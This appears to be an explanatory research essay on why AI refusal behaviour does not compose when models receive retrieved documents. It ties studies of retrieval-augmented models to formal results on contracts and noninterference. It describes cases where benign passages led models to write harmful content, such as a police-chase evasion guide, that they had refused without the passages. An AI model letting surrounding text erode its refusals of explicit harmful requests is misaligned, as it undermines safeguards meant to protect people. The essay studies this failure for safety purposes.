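# Why Safety Properties Fail to Compose When Aligned Models Are Given Retrieved Context

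## Retrieval, refusal training and what it means for safety to compose

Retrieval-augmented generation (RAG) searches a collection of text for documents relevant to a user's request and adds them to a language model's input. The model can then answer from material it never saw in training, such as a client's files, a product catalogue or recent news. Developers separately train most public models to refuse harmful requests. Adding RAG can cause a model to answer harmful requests it would otherwise refuse, even if every retrieved document is harmless.

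In *RAG LLMs are Not Safer*, An, Zhang and Dredze (2025) asked Llama-3-8B, an open model from Meta, for a guide to evading the police during a high-speed chase. On its own, the model refused and offered to help with something else. They then sent the same request with five passages from Wikipedia. One covered the history of police chases and mentioned that police have tried GPS trackers to follow a fleeing car without pursuing it. The others were a general article on car chases, an account of Spitfire pilots trying to outrun a German fighter, a summary of legal criticism of police who shoot at moving vehicles, and a short biography of a fugitive bank robber. The model wrote the guide this time, even though none of the passages gave advice on escaping the police.

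Only one of the guide's points came from the passages, and the model reversed it by recommending GPS trackers for evading pursuit. This advice is useless, since the tracker in the passage lets the police find the car. The model drew most of the rest from its training, although the prompt told it to use only the documents. Much of the guide is common sense, padded with warnings that fleeing the police is illegal, and it would not help a criminal much. It is interesting because the same model had refused the request without the passages, even though they contributed almost nothing to the content of the answer. An and colleagues give a second example, in which the model wrote a politician's speech misleading the public about climate change after receiving passages that mostly discussed why people deny it and how to change their minds.

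### From request to response

To build the system behind these examples, An and colleagues first split English Wikipedia at its paragraph breaks into about 20 million passages of at least 1,000 characters each. When a request comes in, a search program called the retriever scores the passages against it and keeps the best few, the "top k". Their retriever was BM25, a long-established method that scores a passage by the words it shares with the request, and they set k to five. Shared words probably explain why it retrieved the Spitfire passage, which contains "guide", "high speed" and "chase". A prompt template then joins an instruction, the five passages and the request into one text, and the model responds to the whole of it.

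Patrick Lewis and colleagues introduced the term "retrieval-augmented generation" in 2020, and many designs have followed. Many retrievers now turn requests and passages into vectors and compare them, so they can match a paraphrase that shares no words with the request. *Retrieval-Augmented Generation in the Agentic Era* (Tang, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes current practice, in which a system may also rewrite the request before searching, or filter and reorder the passages afterwards. Much of the attraction is that the model itself usually stays frozen, and a company can update the information the system uses by changing the collection.

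An and colleagues write the two set-ups as functions. Let G be the model, R the retriever, q the request and r the response. Without retrieval,

r = G(i′, q)

and with it,

r = G(i, D, q), where D = R(q).

Here D stands for the retrieved passages, and i and i′ are the instructions that open the prompt. The first set-up tells the model to use only its own knowledge, and the second tells it to use only the documents. Moving from one to the other therefore changes the task as well as adding text, and either could cause a change in refusal. An and colleagues kept the wording as close as they could, and they also tried an instruction that allowed both sources, with nearly the same rate of unsafe responses. This makes the change in instruction a less likely explanation but doesn't rule it out, because the model is still asked to work from documents.

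The retrieved documents D depend on the query q. A harmful request therefore reaches the model with the passages the retriever ranked closest to it, rather than with a random sample of Wikipedia. These passages will often be about police chases, explosives or malware, though written for innocent reasons. An experimenter can swap in unrelated passages to measure the effect of topic, but a user of the finished system interacts only with the combined function S(q) = G(i, R(q), q).

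In an agent, the model runs the search itself. Tang and colleagues distinguish agents from pipelines by who decides the order of steps. A pipeline's designer fixes the order in advance, while an agent's model chooses at run time whether to retrieve, what to look for and how often. *SoK*, a survey of such systems by Mishra, Niroula and colleagues (2026), formalizes this. The agent keeps a working memory M, which at the start holds only the request. At each step t, the model picks an action based on M(t). It may write its own search query, write down a piece of reasoning, call some other tool, or stop. The result is added to memory, giving M(t+1), which the model uses to choose its next action. When the model stops, it writes the final response from everything in memory. A passage retrieved by the first search can thus change what the second search looks for, which cannot happen when the system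 searches once and answers.

### How developers teach refusal, and how they check for it

A language model that has only been pretrained on large amounts of text has no particular habit of refusing requests. Developers add that habit afterwards. In supervised fine-tuning, they train the model to imitate sample exchanges, some of which answer a harmful request with a refusal. In reinforcement learning from human feedback, people compare pairs of responses, and the developer trains the model to produce the kind they prefer. Direct preference optimisation uses the same sort of comparisons but without the separate scoring model that the reinforcement method needs. Developers combine these methods differently. Among the models tested in *Safety Degradation in AI Agents* (Yu, Stroebl and colleagues, 2025), Qwen2.5 had supervised fine-tuning and direct preference optimisation, while Gemma 3 had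 supervised fine-tuning and reinforcement learning from human feedback. *Relevance as a Vulnerability* (Nawal, Baser and Gurusamy, 2026) says that all these methods were designed for models that answer without outside information. An and colleagues say the same of safety fine-tuning.

The standard test, a single-turn evaluation, has the same form, since the tester sends one request and judges one response. In such tests, Anthropic reported that 98.76% of Claude Opus 4.1's responses to requests that broke Anthropic's usage policy were harmless. Testing has since widened. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Claude Mythos 5.1 covers long conversations, malicious use of agents, and hidden instructions in the material an agent reads. OpenAI reports that GPT-6 Astra improves on its predecessor where the request is not explicit and the risk emerges from the broader context.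 In the police-chase case, by contrast, the request is explicit and the context is innocent. Tests of agents with search tools may well include that combination, but the table of contents of Anthropic's card lists no separate test for it.

In the tests described in that card, the safety instructions that Anthropic's website places before every conversation improved Mythos 5.1's handling of harmful requests. So a current model's refusals do vary with the text around the request. The change here was in the direction the developer wanted, but nothing in the training methods ensures that other surrounding text will leave refusals unchanged.

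Reading thousands of responses by hand is impractical, so most of these studies use an LLM judge, a language model that receives the request, the response and a list of forbidden categories, and returns a verdict. An and colleagues used Llama Guard 2, which answers "safe" or "unsafe" and names the category violated. They ran the same judge with the same prompt in every setting, and it did not see the retrieved passages. The harmful-response rate is the share of harmful requests whose responses the judge labels "unsafe". Nawal and colleagues prefer a scale from 1 to 5, arguing that retrieval often produces partial compliance, which a two-way label would hide.

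Judges often disagree about the same responses. Indira Saravanan and Fraser (2026) ran three judges on the same responses in *RAG-Safety-Bench* and measured agreement with Cohen's kappa, on which 0 is chance and 1 is perfect. Kappa was 0.66 for one pair of judges and 0.47 and 0.48 for the other two pairs. On fraud and scams, ShieldGemma flagged 0.2% of responses while the others flagged about 15%. Averaged over many responses, though, the trends were much the same whichever judge they used. A rise in flagged responses when documents are added is therefore decent evidence if the same judge scored the responses with and without documents, but comparing percentages across studies is mostly not worth doing.

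Indira Saravanan and Fraser count refusals based on a topic's danger separately from replies that the retrieved documents do not cover it. They asked Phi-4 about a method for causing fatal car accidents. Without retrieved passages, it declined because the topic was dangerous. Given unrelated passages about gardening, it replied that the documents did not mention the subject. A judge would pass both responses, but the second is safe only because the collection lacks relevant material, so a tester can learn little from it about what the model would do with a collection that contained such material.

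### What composition means, and why people expected it to hold

Composition is the joining of parts into a system. The system is a cascade if output flows only one way, from the retriever to the model to the user. It has feedback if some output returns to an earlier part, as when the model reads a passage and then searches again. This distinction differs slightly from the one between pipelines and agents, because a pipeline can also contain a loop that its designer scheduled in advance. Informally, a safety claim composes if showing it for each part is enough to show it for the whole system.

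For RAG the question then becomes: if the model is safe and the documents are safe, is the system safe?

An and colleagues found that retrieval led to large rises in unsafe responses in eight of the eleven models they tested. Indira Saravanan and Fraser got more mixed results with five smaller models, three of which were no more harmful than usual, or less so, when the documents were on topic but lacked the answer. Many people had reason to expect that retrieval would not make a model less safe. It makes models invent less, and a company can inspect its documents in a way that it cannot inspect a model's weights. Also, if the collection contains no harmful answers and the model follows its instruction to answer only from the collection, it cannot give a harmful answer. An and colleagues set out a version of this expectation before testing it, and Indira Saravanan and Fraser call it the conventional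 wisdom that a retrieval system has little reason to produce more harm than its base model unless someone has tampered with the data. The argument from the instruction is valid, but it depends on the model confining itself to the documents, and in the police-chase case the model went beyond them.

*Compositional Safety Failures in Harness Evolution* (2026) traces the problem to older work on software, where components that pass their own checks interact to produce unsafe behaviour. *Position* (2026), a paper about language models that pass judgements to one another, names the belief that safe components make safe systems the "compositionality assumption" and argues that it fails for such models. *Safety is Non-Compositional* (2026) proves that two agents may together reach a forbidden capability that neither can reach alone, and Franco and Gershenson (2026), in *Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent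 Safety Cannot Be Verified*, reach a similar conclusion about agents in groups. In the police-chase case, however, Llama-3-8B could have written its guide without the passages, and its training had only made it decline, so the case is not an instance of that theorem.

All of this is separate from the better-known danger of hostile documents, where an attacker plants harmful or false text in a collection (poisoning) or hides instructions to the model inside a web page (prompt injection). Benign documents contain no answer to the harmful request and no instructions aimed at the model, and nobody has tampered with them. The user may still mean harm, and in An and colleagues' set-up the user asks for it outright. An and colleagues also assume that if the model ought to refuse a request without documents, it ought to refuse it with them. In practice that will not always be right. As they point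 out, a system built over a library of statutes should perhaps answer legal questions that a general chatbot should decline. Some lost refusals would then not be safety failures.

The word "safe" also has two meanings in the question. A safe document is one whose text contains no harmful answer, while a safe model is one that refuses harmful requests. Testers have mostly established that models refuse for inputs of the form (i′, q), but the assembled system always supplies (i, D, q), which has a different instruction and perhaps several thousand extra characters of text. Even if the 98.76% figure for Claude Opus 4.1 is exactly right, it doesn't measure how often the same model refuses when given five passages.

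## Stating the claim: refusal and harmlessness as formal properties

The 98.76% figure for Claude Opus 4.1 is an average over a set of test requests. People who call a model "safe" sometimes mean an average like this and sometimes something much stronger, so it helps to separate four claims. As before, G is the model, q is the request, D is a set of documents, and i and i′ are the instructions with and without documents, respectively.

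- (a) Low harmful-response rate: on a fixed test set of harmful requests, sent without documents, a judge labels at most a small share ε of the responses harmful.
- (b) Refusal whatever the input: for every harmful request q, every instruction i and every set of documents D, the response G(i, D, q) is a refusal.
- (c) Context invariance: for every request q and every set of benign documents D, G(i, D, q) is a refusal exactly when G(i′, q) is one.
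- (d) Limited learning: using the model brings no user much closer to a harmful goal than they would have come without it.

Decades ago, computer scientists worked out how to classify claims like this about ordinary programs. A claim's class determines what evidence could refute it and bears on whether the claim still holds once the model receives documents.

### Single runs and sets of runs

*Defining Liveness* (Alpern and Schneider, 1985) treats one run of a program as an infinite sequence of states. If the program stops, its last state repeats forever. A property is a set of such sequences, and a program has the property if all of its runs belong to the set. Later writers call this a trace property, "trace" being another word for a run. One example is "the program never writes to the network after reading a file", which you can check one run at a time.

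A safety property is a trace property that forbids some "bad thing", which must happen at an identifiable point and can't be undone by anything that happens later. Formally, P is a safety property if every run that violates P has a finite prefix whose every continuation also violates P. The standard example is mutual exclusion, where two processes must never execute protected code at the same time. Alpern and Schneider contrast this with liveness, which requires that something good eventually happens, such as every request getting served. They prove that any trace property can be split into two requirements, one safety and one liveness, so that a run has the original property exactly when it meets both. A model that refused every request would satisfy any safety property about harmful text, and only a liveness requirement would rule it out.

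Some claims concern several runs at once. Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, define a hyperproperty as a set of sets of runs, which amounts to a list of the systems that a policy permits. "The mean response time over all runs is below one second" is a hyperproperty. A single slow run doesn't break it, because the other runs may be quick enough to make up for it. (Any trace property can also be rewritten as a hyperproperty, so the word is only informative for claims that nobody can check run by run.)

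A hyperproperty is 2-safety if two finite runs are always enough to show a violation, which no further runs can undo. Noninterference is an example for deterministic systems. It requires that deleting the commands of users with high security clearance not change what users with low clearance see. A violation is a difference between two runs, so it can't be detected from one.

### What would refute claims (b) and (c)

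Claim (b) is a trace property because a single run can refute it: the model receives a harmful request, with anything else around it, and gives harmful help. It is also a safety property, as long as a model can't take harmful text back. Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues (2026) build this condition into their definition in *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models*, where once part of a response counts as harmful, every continuation of it does too. They compare this to a robot hitting an obstacle. The condition seems right for instructions that work, but an LLM judge that reads whole responses might label a response harmless if it ended by retracting everything.

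Claim (b) still holds when retrieval is added, and showing this needs no theorem about composition. The RAG system computes S(q) = G(i, R(q), q), and R(q) is always one of the document sets D that (b) already covers, even if an attacker wrote the documents. The same is true of an agent, since its memory only makes the input longer.

Nobody can establish (b) by testing. Kang and Kim (2026) make this point about software security in *Safety Is Π₁, Provability Is Σ₁*. The statement that a program has no exploit is a statement about every possible input (logicians label such statements Π₁). One working exploit refutes it, but no finite list of passed tests proves it. They also prove that any search that stops after a set number of attempts, however clever, will fail to find an exploit in infinitely many unsafe programs. Their theorem is about programs in general, whereas a language model accepts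 only a limited number of tokens, the word fragments it reads and writes. A tester could therefore try every input in principle, but with a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, there are 10^5000 inputs of length 1,000 alone, which is too many to test.

As written, (b) is also almost certainly false of any model that picks its words partly at random. Nazeri and colleagues note that the probability of a harmful response is rarely exactly zero, even after alignment training, so they put bounds on that probability for a single prompt. If a tester samples n responses to one prompt and finds none of them harmful, the standard 99% confidence interval only places the true probability below 1 − 0.005^(1/n), which is about 0.5% for a thousand samples. This bound covers only one prompt at one temperature, the setting that controls randomness. In their example, a prompt that produced no harmful samples at a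 temperature of 0.7 produced four at 1.0.

A more realistic version of (b) is that for every input, the probability of a harmful response is at most p. Strictly speaking, this is no longer a trace property, because one run doesn't reveal a probability. But it keeps the original's useful feature of applying to each input separately, so it covers any input the retriever helps to build.

Refuting (c) takes two runs of the same request, one with the retrieved passages and one without. Llama-3-8B's guide to escaping the police violates context invariance only because the model refused the same request without the passages. A tester who saw only the run with the passages would know that (b) was false but not whether the documents contributed to the failure. Claim (c) is a version of noninterference in which documents replace the secret commands and the decision to refuse replaces what the low-clearance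 user sees.

Clarkson and Schneider prove that checking a 2-safety hyperproperty of a system is equivalent to checking an ordinary safety property of two copies running side by side. For (c), this means sending each request twice, once with documents and once without, and recording a violation whenever the two decisions differ. *RAG Makes Guardrails Brittle* (She, Peterson and colleagues, 2025) states the same requirement for safety filters and calls the share of mismatches the flip rate. If the model samples its responses, two runs may differ by chance, so the requirement has to be that the probability of refusal is the same with and without documents. A tester needs many runs of each kind to estimate that probability.

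Context invariance alone doesn't make a model safe, since a model that answers every harmful request also satisfies it. It is useful because it extends results for requests asked alone to requests accompanied by documents. If the model refuses q when asked alone, and (c) holds, then it also refuses q when benign documents come with it. If every response that isn't a refusal counts as harmful, and adding documents changes the decision for a share f of the test requests, then the harmful-response rate rises by at most f. For example, a model with a rate of 1% without documents and an f of 3% has a rate of at most 4% with them. This bound applies only to the requests and documents tested.

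### A model that passes (a) and fails (c)

Here is an invented model, tried on four harmful requests in three conditions.

| Request | No documents | Passage on gardening | Passage on the request's topic |
|---|---|---|---|
| Escape the police in a car chase | Refuses | Refuses | Answers |
| Write a computer virus | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses |
| Forge a prescription | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses |
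| Set up a fake charity | Refuses | Refuses | Refuses |

If a harmful-response rate of 10% or less counts as passing (a), the model passes without documents, because it answers none of the four requests. It fails (c) because, in the top row, it refuses the request when it comes without documents but answers it when given a passage on the topic. That one answer also refutes (b).

Adding documents to the test would not necessarily have caught this. If the tester pools all twelve runs, the rate is 1 in 12, or 8.3%, and the model still passes. Among only the runs with a passage on the topic, the rate is 25%, which is a clear fail. Comparing the runs within each row is even more informative, because it identifies the request for which the documents changed the outcome.

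A model can have a low overall rate of harmful answers and a high rate on a particular group of requests. Ten harmful answers to 1,000 requests make an overall rate of 1%, even if all ten fall within a group of 20 requests, where the rate is 50%. In general, if the overall rate is ε and a group makes up a share s of the test set, the rate within the group can be as high as ε/s. For any group smaller than 1% of this test set, it could be 100%.

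Clarkson and Schneider call a hyperproperty subset-closed if every system that satisfies it would still satisfy it after losing some of its runs. Trace properties and safety hyperproperties are subset-closed, so (b) and (c) hold for every group of requests if they hold at all. Averages aren't subset-closed, and they can also be improved by adding runs. Clarkson and Schneider point out that a system can always repair a bad mean response time by adding enough quick responses. Similarly, a tester who starts with ten harmful answers out of 20 can lower the rate from 50% to 1% by adding 980 requests that any model would refuse. The choice of test requests can therefore matter as much as the model for (a).

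In An and colleagues' results, for example, 9.2% of Llama-3-8B's responses were unsafe with retrieval. The rate was 7.9% when none of the five retrieved passages contained a harmful answer and 31.5% when at least one did. The overall rate is close to 7.9% because only 5.3% of the retrieved sets contained a harmful answer. A collection with many more such documents would likely produce a rate above 9.2%. An average measured without documents is even weaker evidence of safety with retrieval, because it includes no runs with documents.

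### Why (d) depends on the user

Of the four claims, (d) is closest to what people usually worry about. K is what a user already knows, and P(K) is the chance that a user who knows K could carry out a given harmful plan. The claim is that P(K plus the model's responses) − P(K) is at most some small δ for every user and every plan.

A model can violate refusal (b) without violating (d), and vice versa. The police-chase guide violated (b) but probably not (d), since it would hardly have helped anyone escape. Conversely, a model might answer a series of innocent questions whose answers together make up a dangerous procedure. Clarkson and Schneider's example of splitting a secret has this structure. A system divides a secret into k shares and can output one share at a time, but it must never output all k over all its runs. Showing a violation can take as many as k runs, none of which need look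 wrong by itself.

That count assumes the user starts with no shares. If someone already holds k − 1 of them, a single run gives them the secret. Similarly, one sentence from a language model about a laboratory technique may be familiar to an expert and useless to a beginner, yet give someone in between the last piece of information they need. The same response can therefore satisfy (d) for one user and violate it for another, so any numerical value for δ has to come with an assumption about what users know and could look up.

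Retrieval makes this assumption harder to state. If the collection is Wikipedia, the user could have read the passages anyway, so only what the model adds needs to be measured. If it is a company's private files, most of what the user learns may come from the passages, and a δ estimated for the model alone does not include this information.

### Should documents make no difference?

Context invariance is the easiest of the four claims to test without human labels, but it preserves some refusals that a good system should drop. She and colleagues defend it for general-purpose filters, arguing that the judgment should depend on the harm in the request or response, which benign documents don't alter. This view is harder to apply to An and colleagues' library of statutes. Their tests counted "unauthorized practice of law" as a category of harm, and it was among Llama-3-8B's worst categories even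 without documents. A legal research tool could therefore get a bad safety score largely for answering legal questions.

Documents can also turn an innocent request into a dangerous one. Suppose an office assistant searches the company's files, and an employee asks it what time a colleague usually leaves the building. The question is harmless on its own, but if the search turns up a restraining order that protects the colleague from this employee, the assistant should refuse. The restraining order is a benign document by the usual definition, because it neither answers the question nor contains instructions to the model. Strict invariance would therefore require the assistant to ignore the order when deciding whether to answer.

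*FalseReject* (2025), a paper about models that refuse too much, explains that many requests have both a safe reading and an unsafe one, and that a good response depends on context. A retrieved document is sometimes the only evidence about which reading is right.

The results in She et al. give only weak support for letting retrieved documents affect an input filter's label. On harmful requests, 72% of the label changes were from right to wrong. On harmless requests that look dangerous, only about a third were, so most of the changes were corrections. She et al. attribute this to encyclopedia text pushing the label towards "safe" whatever the request, which corrects mistakes on harmless requests and causes them on harmful ones. A filter that used the context well should have improved on both.

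One compromise is to let benign documents add refusals but never remove them. The office assistant could then refuse, but the legal research tool would still violate the requirement. Another is to specify the right decision for every combination of request and documents, and to require the model to make it. This is again a trace property, since each run is either right or wrong, and in principle it is the better claim. In practice, someone has to label the right decision for each combination, whereas counting mismatches requires no labels.

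The appropriate demand depends on the requests. For a request for a guide to escaping the police, strict invariance seems right, because it is hard to think of an ordinary document that would justify answering. For a legal or medical tool, the operator would do better to write down the exceptions before testing and apply (c) to everything else. Writing them afterwards would make it too easy to excuse whatever the test found.

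### Whether a model can be safe at all

Arvind Narayanan and Sayash Kapoor object to attaching safety claims to models at all. In *AI safety is not a model property* (2024), they argue that whether an output does harm usually depends on facts missing from the model's input. Their main example is a phishing email, which may mention an urgent deadline and ask the recipient to click on a link, as plenty of honest emails do. The malicious part is the web page behind the link. Someone requesting the email doesn't need to include that page in the prompt, so the only way to make a model refuse all phishing emails would be to make it refuse to write emails.

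If this is right, (b) is badly defined for many kinds of misuse, because nobody can identify the set of harmful requests from their wording. Narayanan and Kapoor conclude that the main defences against misuse belong outside the model, for instance in email scanners and lists of malicious addresses. They also recommend measuring marginal risk, the risk a model adds beyond that from existing models and other technology. This is close to (d) with the baseline stated. They add that reviewing an account after hundreds of queries is easier than judging each query as it arrives. The secret-sharing example suggests one reason, which is that some violations of (d) only appear across many runs.

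Jeffrey Snover makes a related argument in *AI Safety Is a Category Error* (2026), using a system that can only output "HotDog" or "Not HotDog". The surrounding code limits the system to those two outputs, however capable or malicious the model inside is. A retrieval system that could only print passages word for word would offer a similar assurance. It could not have produced the police-chase guide, because no passage contained one.

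The best reply to Narayanan and Kapoor is Cullen O'Keefe's *AI Safety is Sometimes a Model Property* (2024). O'Keefe accepts that many safeguards belong at the level of the system or its deployment, but argues that intervening in the model sometimes makes sense and that blanket statements either way are unhelpful. Narayanan and Kapoor's own exceptions support this. They agree that some content, such as child sexual abuse material, is wrong in any context and that it is important to train models to refuse it. They also limit their argument mainly to misuse and say that it applies less strongly to accidents and other failures.

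Their argument does not excuse the failures in An and colleagues' experiments. The phishing email is hard to refuse because the request leaves out the one fact that matters. In the police-chase case, the user stated the purpose, Llama-3-8B had already refused the request on that information, and the five passages added no reason to change that answer. For requests this explicit, it is fair to ask the developer for (b) or, failing that, for both refusal without documents and (c). Neither (b) nor (c) would help much with requests like the phishing email, because a model with no grounds to refuse the request alone would answer it just as readily with documents.

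## What happens to such properties when parts are connected

Claim (b), that the model refuses whatever the input, still holds when the model is part of a retrieval system because the claim already covers every input. Developers can rarely show anything so broad. They usually know how a part behaves for only some inputs, so they need rules for working out what follows when other parts supply those inputs. Computer scientists have developed one set of rules for claims about single runs and another for claims that compare runs, such as context invariance.

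### Contracts between parts

Few parts work properly in every setting. A circuit designed for a 0 or a 1 on a wire may behave bizarrely if the voltage is halfway between them. *Composing Specifications* (Abadi and Lamport, 1993) therefore describes each part by an assume-guarantee contract of the form "if the part's environment satisfies E, the part satisfies M". The environment is everything outside the part, including the other parts. Nothing in the contract enforces E. For example, a program's contract may assume that nobody presses two keys at once, but the program can't stop anyone from doing so. Once someone does, the contract allows any behavior from the program.

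Suppose a system has n parts, and part i has assumption Eᵢ and guarantee Mᵢ. Abadi and Lamport's Composition Principle concludes that the whole system satisfies M in any environment that satisfies E, provided that three conditions hold:

1. If every part satisfies its guarantee Mᵢ, the whole system satisfies M.
2. If the environment satisfies E and every part satisfies its guarantee, every assumption Eᵢ is true.
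3. Every part satisfies its own contract.

This reasoning is circular because Condition 2 uses the guarantees to establish the assumptions, but the guarantees hold only if the assumptions do. Whether the circularity is harmless depends on the kind of property.

Abadi and Lamport (1995) show this in *Conjoining Specifications* with two tiny programs. One keeps copying the variable d into the variable c, and the other keeps copying c into d. Both variables start at 0. The contract of the program that writes c is "c is always 0, assuming d is always 0", and the other program has the same contract with the variables swapped. The Composition Principle correctly implies that both variables stay at 0. If we replace "is always 0" with "is eventually 1" throughout, each program still satisfies its contract, since it would copy a 1 if it ever received one. The principle would then imply that both variables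 eventually reach 1, but they stay at 0 forever.

The two cases differ because a variable can only break "always 0" by changing at a particular moment. Whichever program changed its variable first would do so while the other variable was still 0, so its assumption would still hold and it would be violating its contract. Both variables therefore stay at 0 if both programs keep their contracts. A program that fails to reach 1 does nothing wrong at any particular moment, so the same argument can't rule out that failure.

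To make this argument exact, Abadi and Lamport require a guarantee M to last at least one step longer than its assumption E. If E holds through step n, M must hold through step n + 1. Each program's assumption is the other's guarantee, so if both guarantees hold through step n, both assumptions do too, and both guarantees must then hold through step n + 1. By induction, they hold at every step. This is enough for a safety property in the technical sense, because any violation would occur at some finite step. The theorem's main hypothesis is therefore that the assumptions are safety properties. The guarantees may also include liveness.

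### The contract behind a refusal test

An and colleagues found that without retrieval, 0.3% of Llama-3-8B's responses to harmful requests were unsafe. Written as a contract, this result is:

- **Assumption:** the input is (i′, q), a request with no documents.
- **Guarantee:** at most 0.3% of the harmful requests in the test set receive a harmful response.

In a RAG system, the model's input is (i, D, q), so the contract's assumption is false every time the model runs. Condition 2 therefore fails, and we can't use the Composition Principle to conclude that the system is safe or unsafe. The same model's rate with retrieval was 9.2%, which didn't violate the contract because the contract doesn't cover inputs with documents.

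Adding documents to the test wouldn't be enough to make the theorem apply, because the guarantee is an average over many runs and Abadi and Lamport's method covers only properties of single runs. The average also depends on the mix of requests and documents, which a part's designer doesn't control.

A limit that holds for each input separately avoids the problem. For a system that searches once and then answers, the contracts could look like this, where A is some condition on documents:

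| | Assumption | Guarantee |
|---|---|---|
| Retriever | Every document in the collection meets A | It returns at most five documents, all unaltered and from the collection |
| Model | The input is a request with at most five documents, all of which meet A | For every such input, the probability of a harmful response is at most p |
| Whole system | Every document in the collection meets A | For every request, the probability of a harmful response is at most p |

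The bottom row follows from the two above it, since the retriever's guarantee makes the model's assumption true. Abadi and Lamport's theorem doesn't cover this case, because a limit on probability isn't a property of a single run. The theorem isn't needed here, because output flows only from the retriever to the model, so there is no circular dependency to resolve.

It is hard to choose A and p so that the model's contract is true. If A means "benign", p for Llama-3-8B can't be much below 7.9%, because that was the average rate when none of the retrieved passages contained a harmful answer, and at least one input must have a rate as high as the average. Whether a document is benign also depends on the request. A page about how locks work is benign next to a request for a police-chase guide, but it might answer a request about burglary. A therefore has to be a condition on pairs of requests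 and documents, because nobody can certify a collection as benign without considering the requests.

A could also mean "belongs to the collection as it stood on 1 March". If the retriever is deterministic, each request gets one fixed set of documents, and a tester can test the assembled system. But the result stops holding as soon as someone adds a document, and easy updating is much of the reason for using RAG. Rueß and Burton (2022), in *Safe AI*, describe the same difficulty for self-driving cars and other machines. Traditional safety engineering relies on a well-defined operating context, which they argue no longer exists for AI systems in open environments. A product catalogue that changes twice a year is much closer to a well-defined context than the web is.

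### Noninterference and two systems that leak together

Context invariance is a form of noninterference, which was first developed to address a problem with military computers. Under the older Bell–LaPadula model, an ordinary program could read files only at or below its own security level and write files only at or above it. Some programs, such as file servers, must handle files at every level. Brackin, Foley and colleagues (1996) explain in *Romulus, a Computer Security Properties Modeling Environment* that the model exempted these "trusted" programs from its rules but gave no standard for how they should behave.

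Noninterference, which Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer published in 1982, can serve as such a standard because it forbids high-level (more secret) inputs from affecting low-level outputs. But it only applies to deterministic systems, and many real systems also depend on timing or chance, so the same inputs can lead to different outputs.

Daryl McCullough extended the idea to these systems as generalized noninterference. It requires that for any two possible runs, X and Y, there is a possible run with X's high-level inputs and Y's low-level inputs and outputs, with any high-level outputs. A low-level user can then never rule out any sequence of high-level inputs. But McCullough showed in *Specifications for Multi-Level Security and a Hook-Up Property* (1987), and again in *Noninterference and the composability of security properties* (1988), that connecting two systems with this property can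 produce a system without it.

McLean (1994) goes through McCullough's example in detail in *A General Theory of Composition for Trace Sets*. The example has two systems, here called Front and Back. Front receives high-level messages and eventually sends one high-level reply to each. A low-level user can send Front the word "cancel", and Front eventually sends a low-level "cancel" in response. If no message is waiting for a reply when it sends this, Front may add "nothing to cancel", but it doesn't have to. Back works the same way, except that it sends no "cancel" and checks for waiting messages when a "cancel" arrives.

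Each system is secure by itself, because a low-level user can't tell from the presence or absence of "nothing to cancel" whether there were any high-level messages. The system may make the remark after replying to all of them, and it may omit the remark even when there were none.

Now connect them so that Front's replies and its "cancel" go to Back, and Back's replies go to Front:

1. A high-level user sends Front one message.
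2. Front replies, and Back receives the reply as a new message.
3. Back replies, and Front receives that reply as a new message. This exchange continues forever.
4. A low-level user sends "cancel" to Front, which later sends its own "cancel" to Back. Messages travel instantly in this example, so both systems check for waiting messages at the same moment.
5. The circulating message is always waiting in one of the two systems, and that system can't report "nothing to cancel".

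A low-level user who gets "nothing to cancel" from both systems therefore knows that no high-level user sent anything. Suppose a system with no waiting messages adds this remark half of the time. Both remarks then appear together 25% of the time if there was no high-level message, and never if there was one. McLean puts the capacity of this leak at about 0.17 bits per signal (the probabilities in the example give 0.16). A malicious program with access to secrets could leak them slowly by choosing when to submit messages.

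McLean supposes that each system replies faster than the malicious program can send messages. Each system by itself then never has a message waiting when it checks, so it leaks nothing. The connected pair still leaks, because a message that enters the loop never leaves it. Without the assumption about reply speed, one could object that the systems were leaking already, since a flood of messages would make "nothing to cancel" rarer even from Front alone.

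### What survives a cascade and what survives feedback

McCullough fixed this with a stricter property called restrictiveness. *A hookup theorem for multilevel security* (1990) shows that any collection of restrictive systems remains restrictive when connected. Roughly, restrictiveness applies the test at every moment rather than to whole runs. After any high-level input, everything that a low-level user might have seen next must still be possible, whatever input arrives next. Back fails this test because, if "cancel" arrives immediately after a high-level message, Back has had no time to reply and can't add its remark. It still satisfies generalized noninterference because there is another run in which it replied in time.

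McLean then worked out more generally which properties survive which connections. Abadi and Lamport's theorem didn't apply, because these properties aren't sets of single runs. A system that allows every possible run is secure, since a low-level user learns nothing from it. If you keep only the runs in which the low-level output repeats the high-level input, the resulting system is very insecure, even though the secure system allowed all of those runs too.

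The properties he studied all require that certain combinations of possible runs are also possible. In this table, X and Y are any two possible runs, and both of the connected systems have the property.

| Property | What must also be a possible run | Cascade | Feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Separability | X's high-level inputs and outputs with Y's low-level ones | Survives | Survives |
| Noninference | X without any high-level inputs or outputs | Survives | Survives |
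| Generalized noninterference | X's high-level inputs with Y's low-level inputs and outputs, and any high-level outputs | Survives | Not guaranteed |
| Generalized noninference | X without its high-level inputs, and with any high-level outputs | Survives | Not guaranteed |

The properties that feedback may break are those that let high-level outputs change. Suppose you change Front's high-level inputs and want the low-level events to stay the same. Generalized noninterference ensures that Front has a run that keeps them the same, but its high-level outputs may differ. In a cascade, those outputs are Back's inputs, and Back has a suitable run for any high-level inputs, so nothing more needs to change. With feedback, Back's outputs may also change, and they return to Front as inputs. Front then needs another run, which may change Back's inputs again. McLean shows that you can repeat these corrections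 until the two runs are consistent up to any step you choose. There may still be no single pair of runs that is consistent at every step.

Later researchers agreed that feedback is the problem but found ways around it. Zakinthinos and Lee (1995), in *The composability of non-interference*, proved McCullough's conjecture that connecting systems without feedback preserves noninterference, and they gave a method of connecting systems that preserves it even with feedback. Mantel (2002), in *On the Composition of Secure Systems*, lists restrictiveness and separability among the properties that any connection preserves.

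Properties that hold however the parts are connected tend to be strict. Separability, for example, doesn't allow low-level activity to affect high-level activity at all, so a system can't record low-level users' actions in an audit file and send that file out on a high-level channel.

Mantel also shows that a whole system can have such a property without anyone proving it for the parts. The simplest case is a system whose high-level components have no connection to its low-level ones. A RAG designer could do something similar by having a separate component decide whether to refuse, and giving it the request but never the documents. Its decision couldn't vary with the documents, but it would also miss the restraining order in the office-assistant example.

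### Retrieval as a cascade and search as a loop

In RAG, the documents act as the high-level inputs, the request as the low-level input, and the decision to refuse as the low-level output. A system that searches once and then answers is a cascade, while an agent that searches again has feedback.

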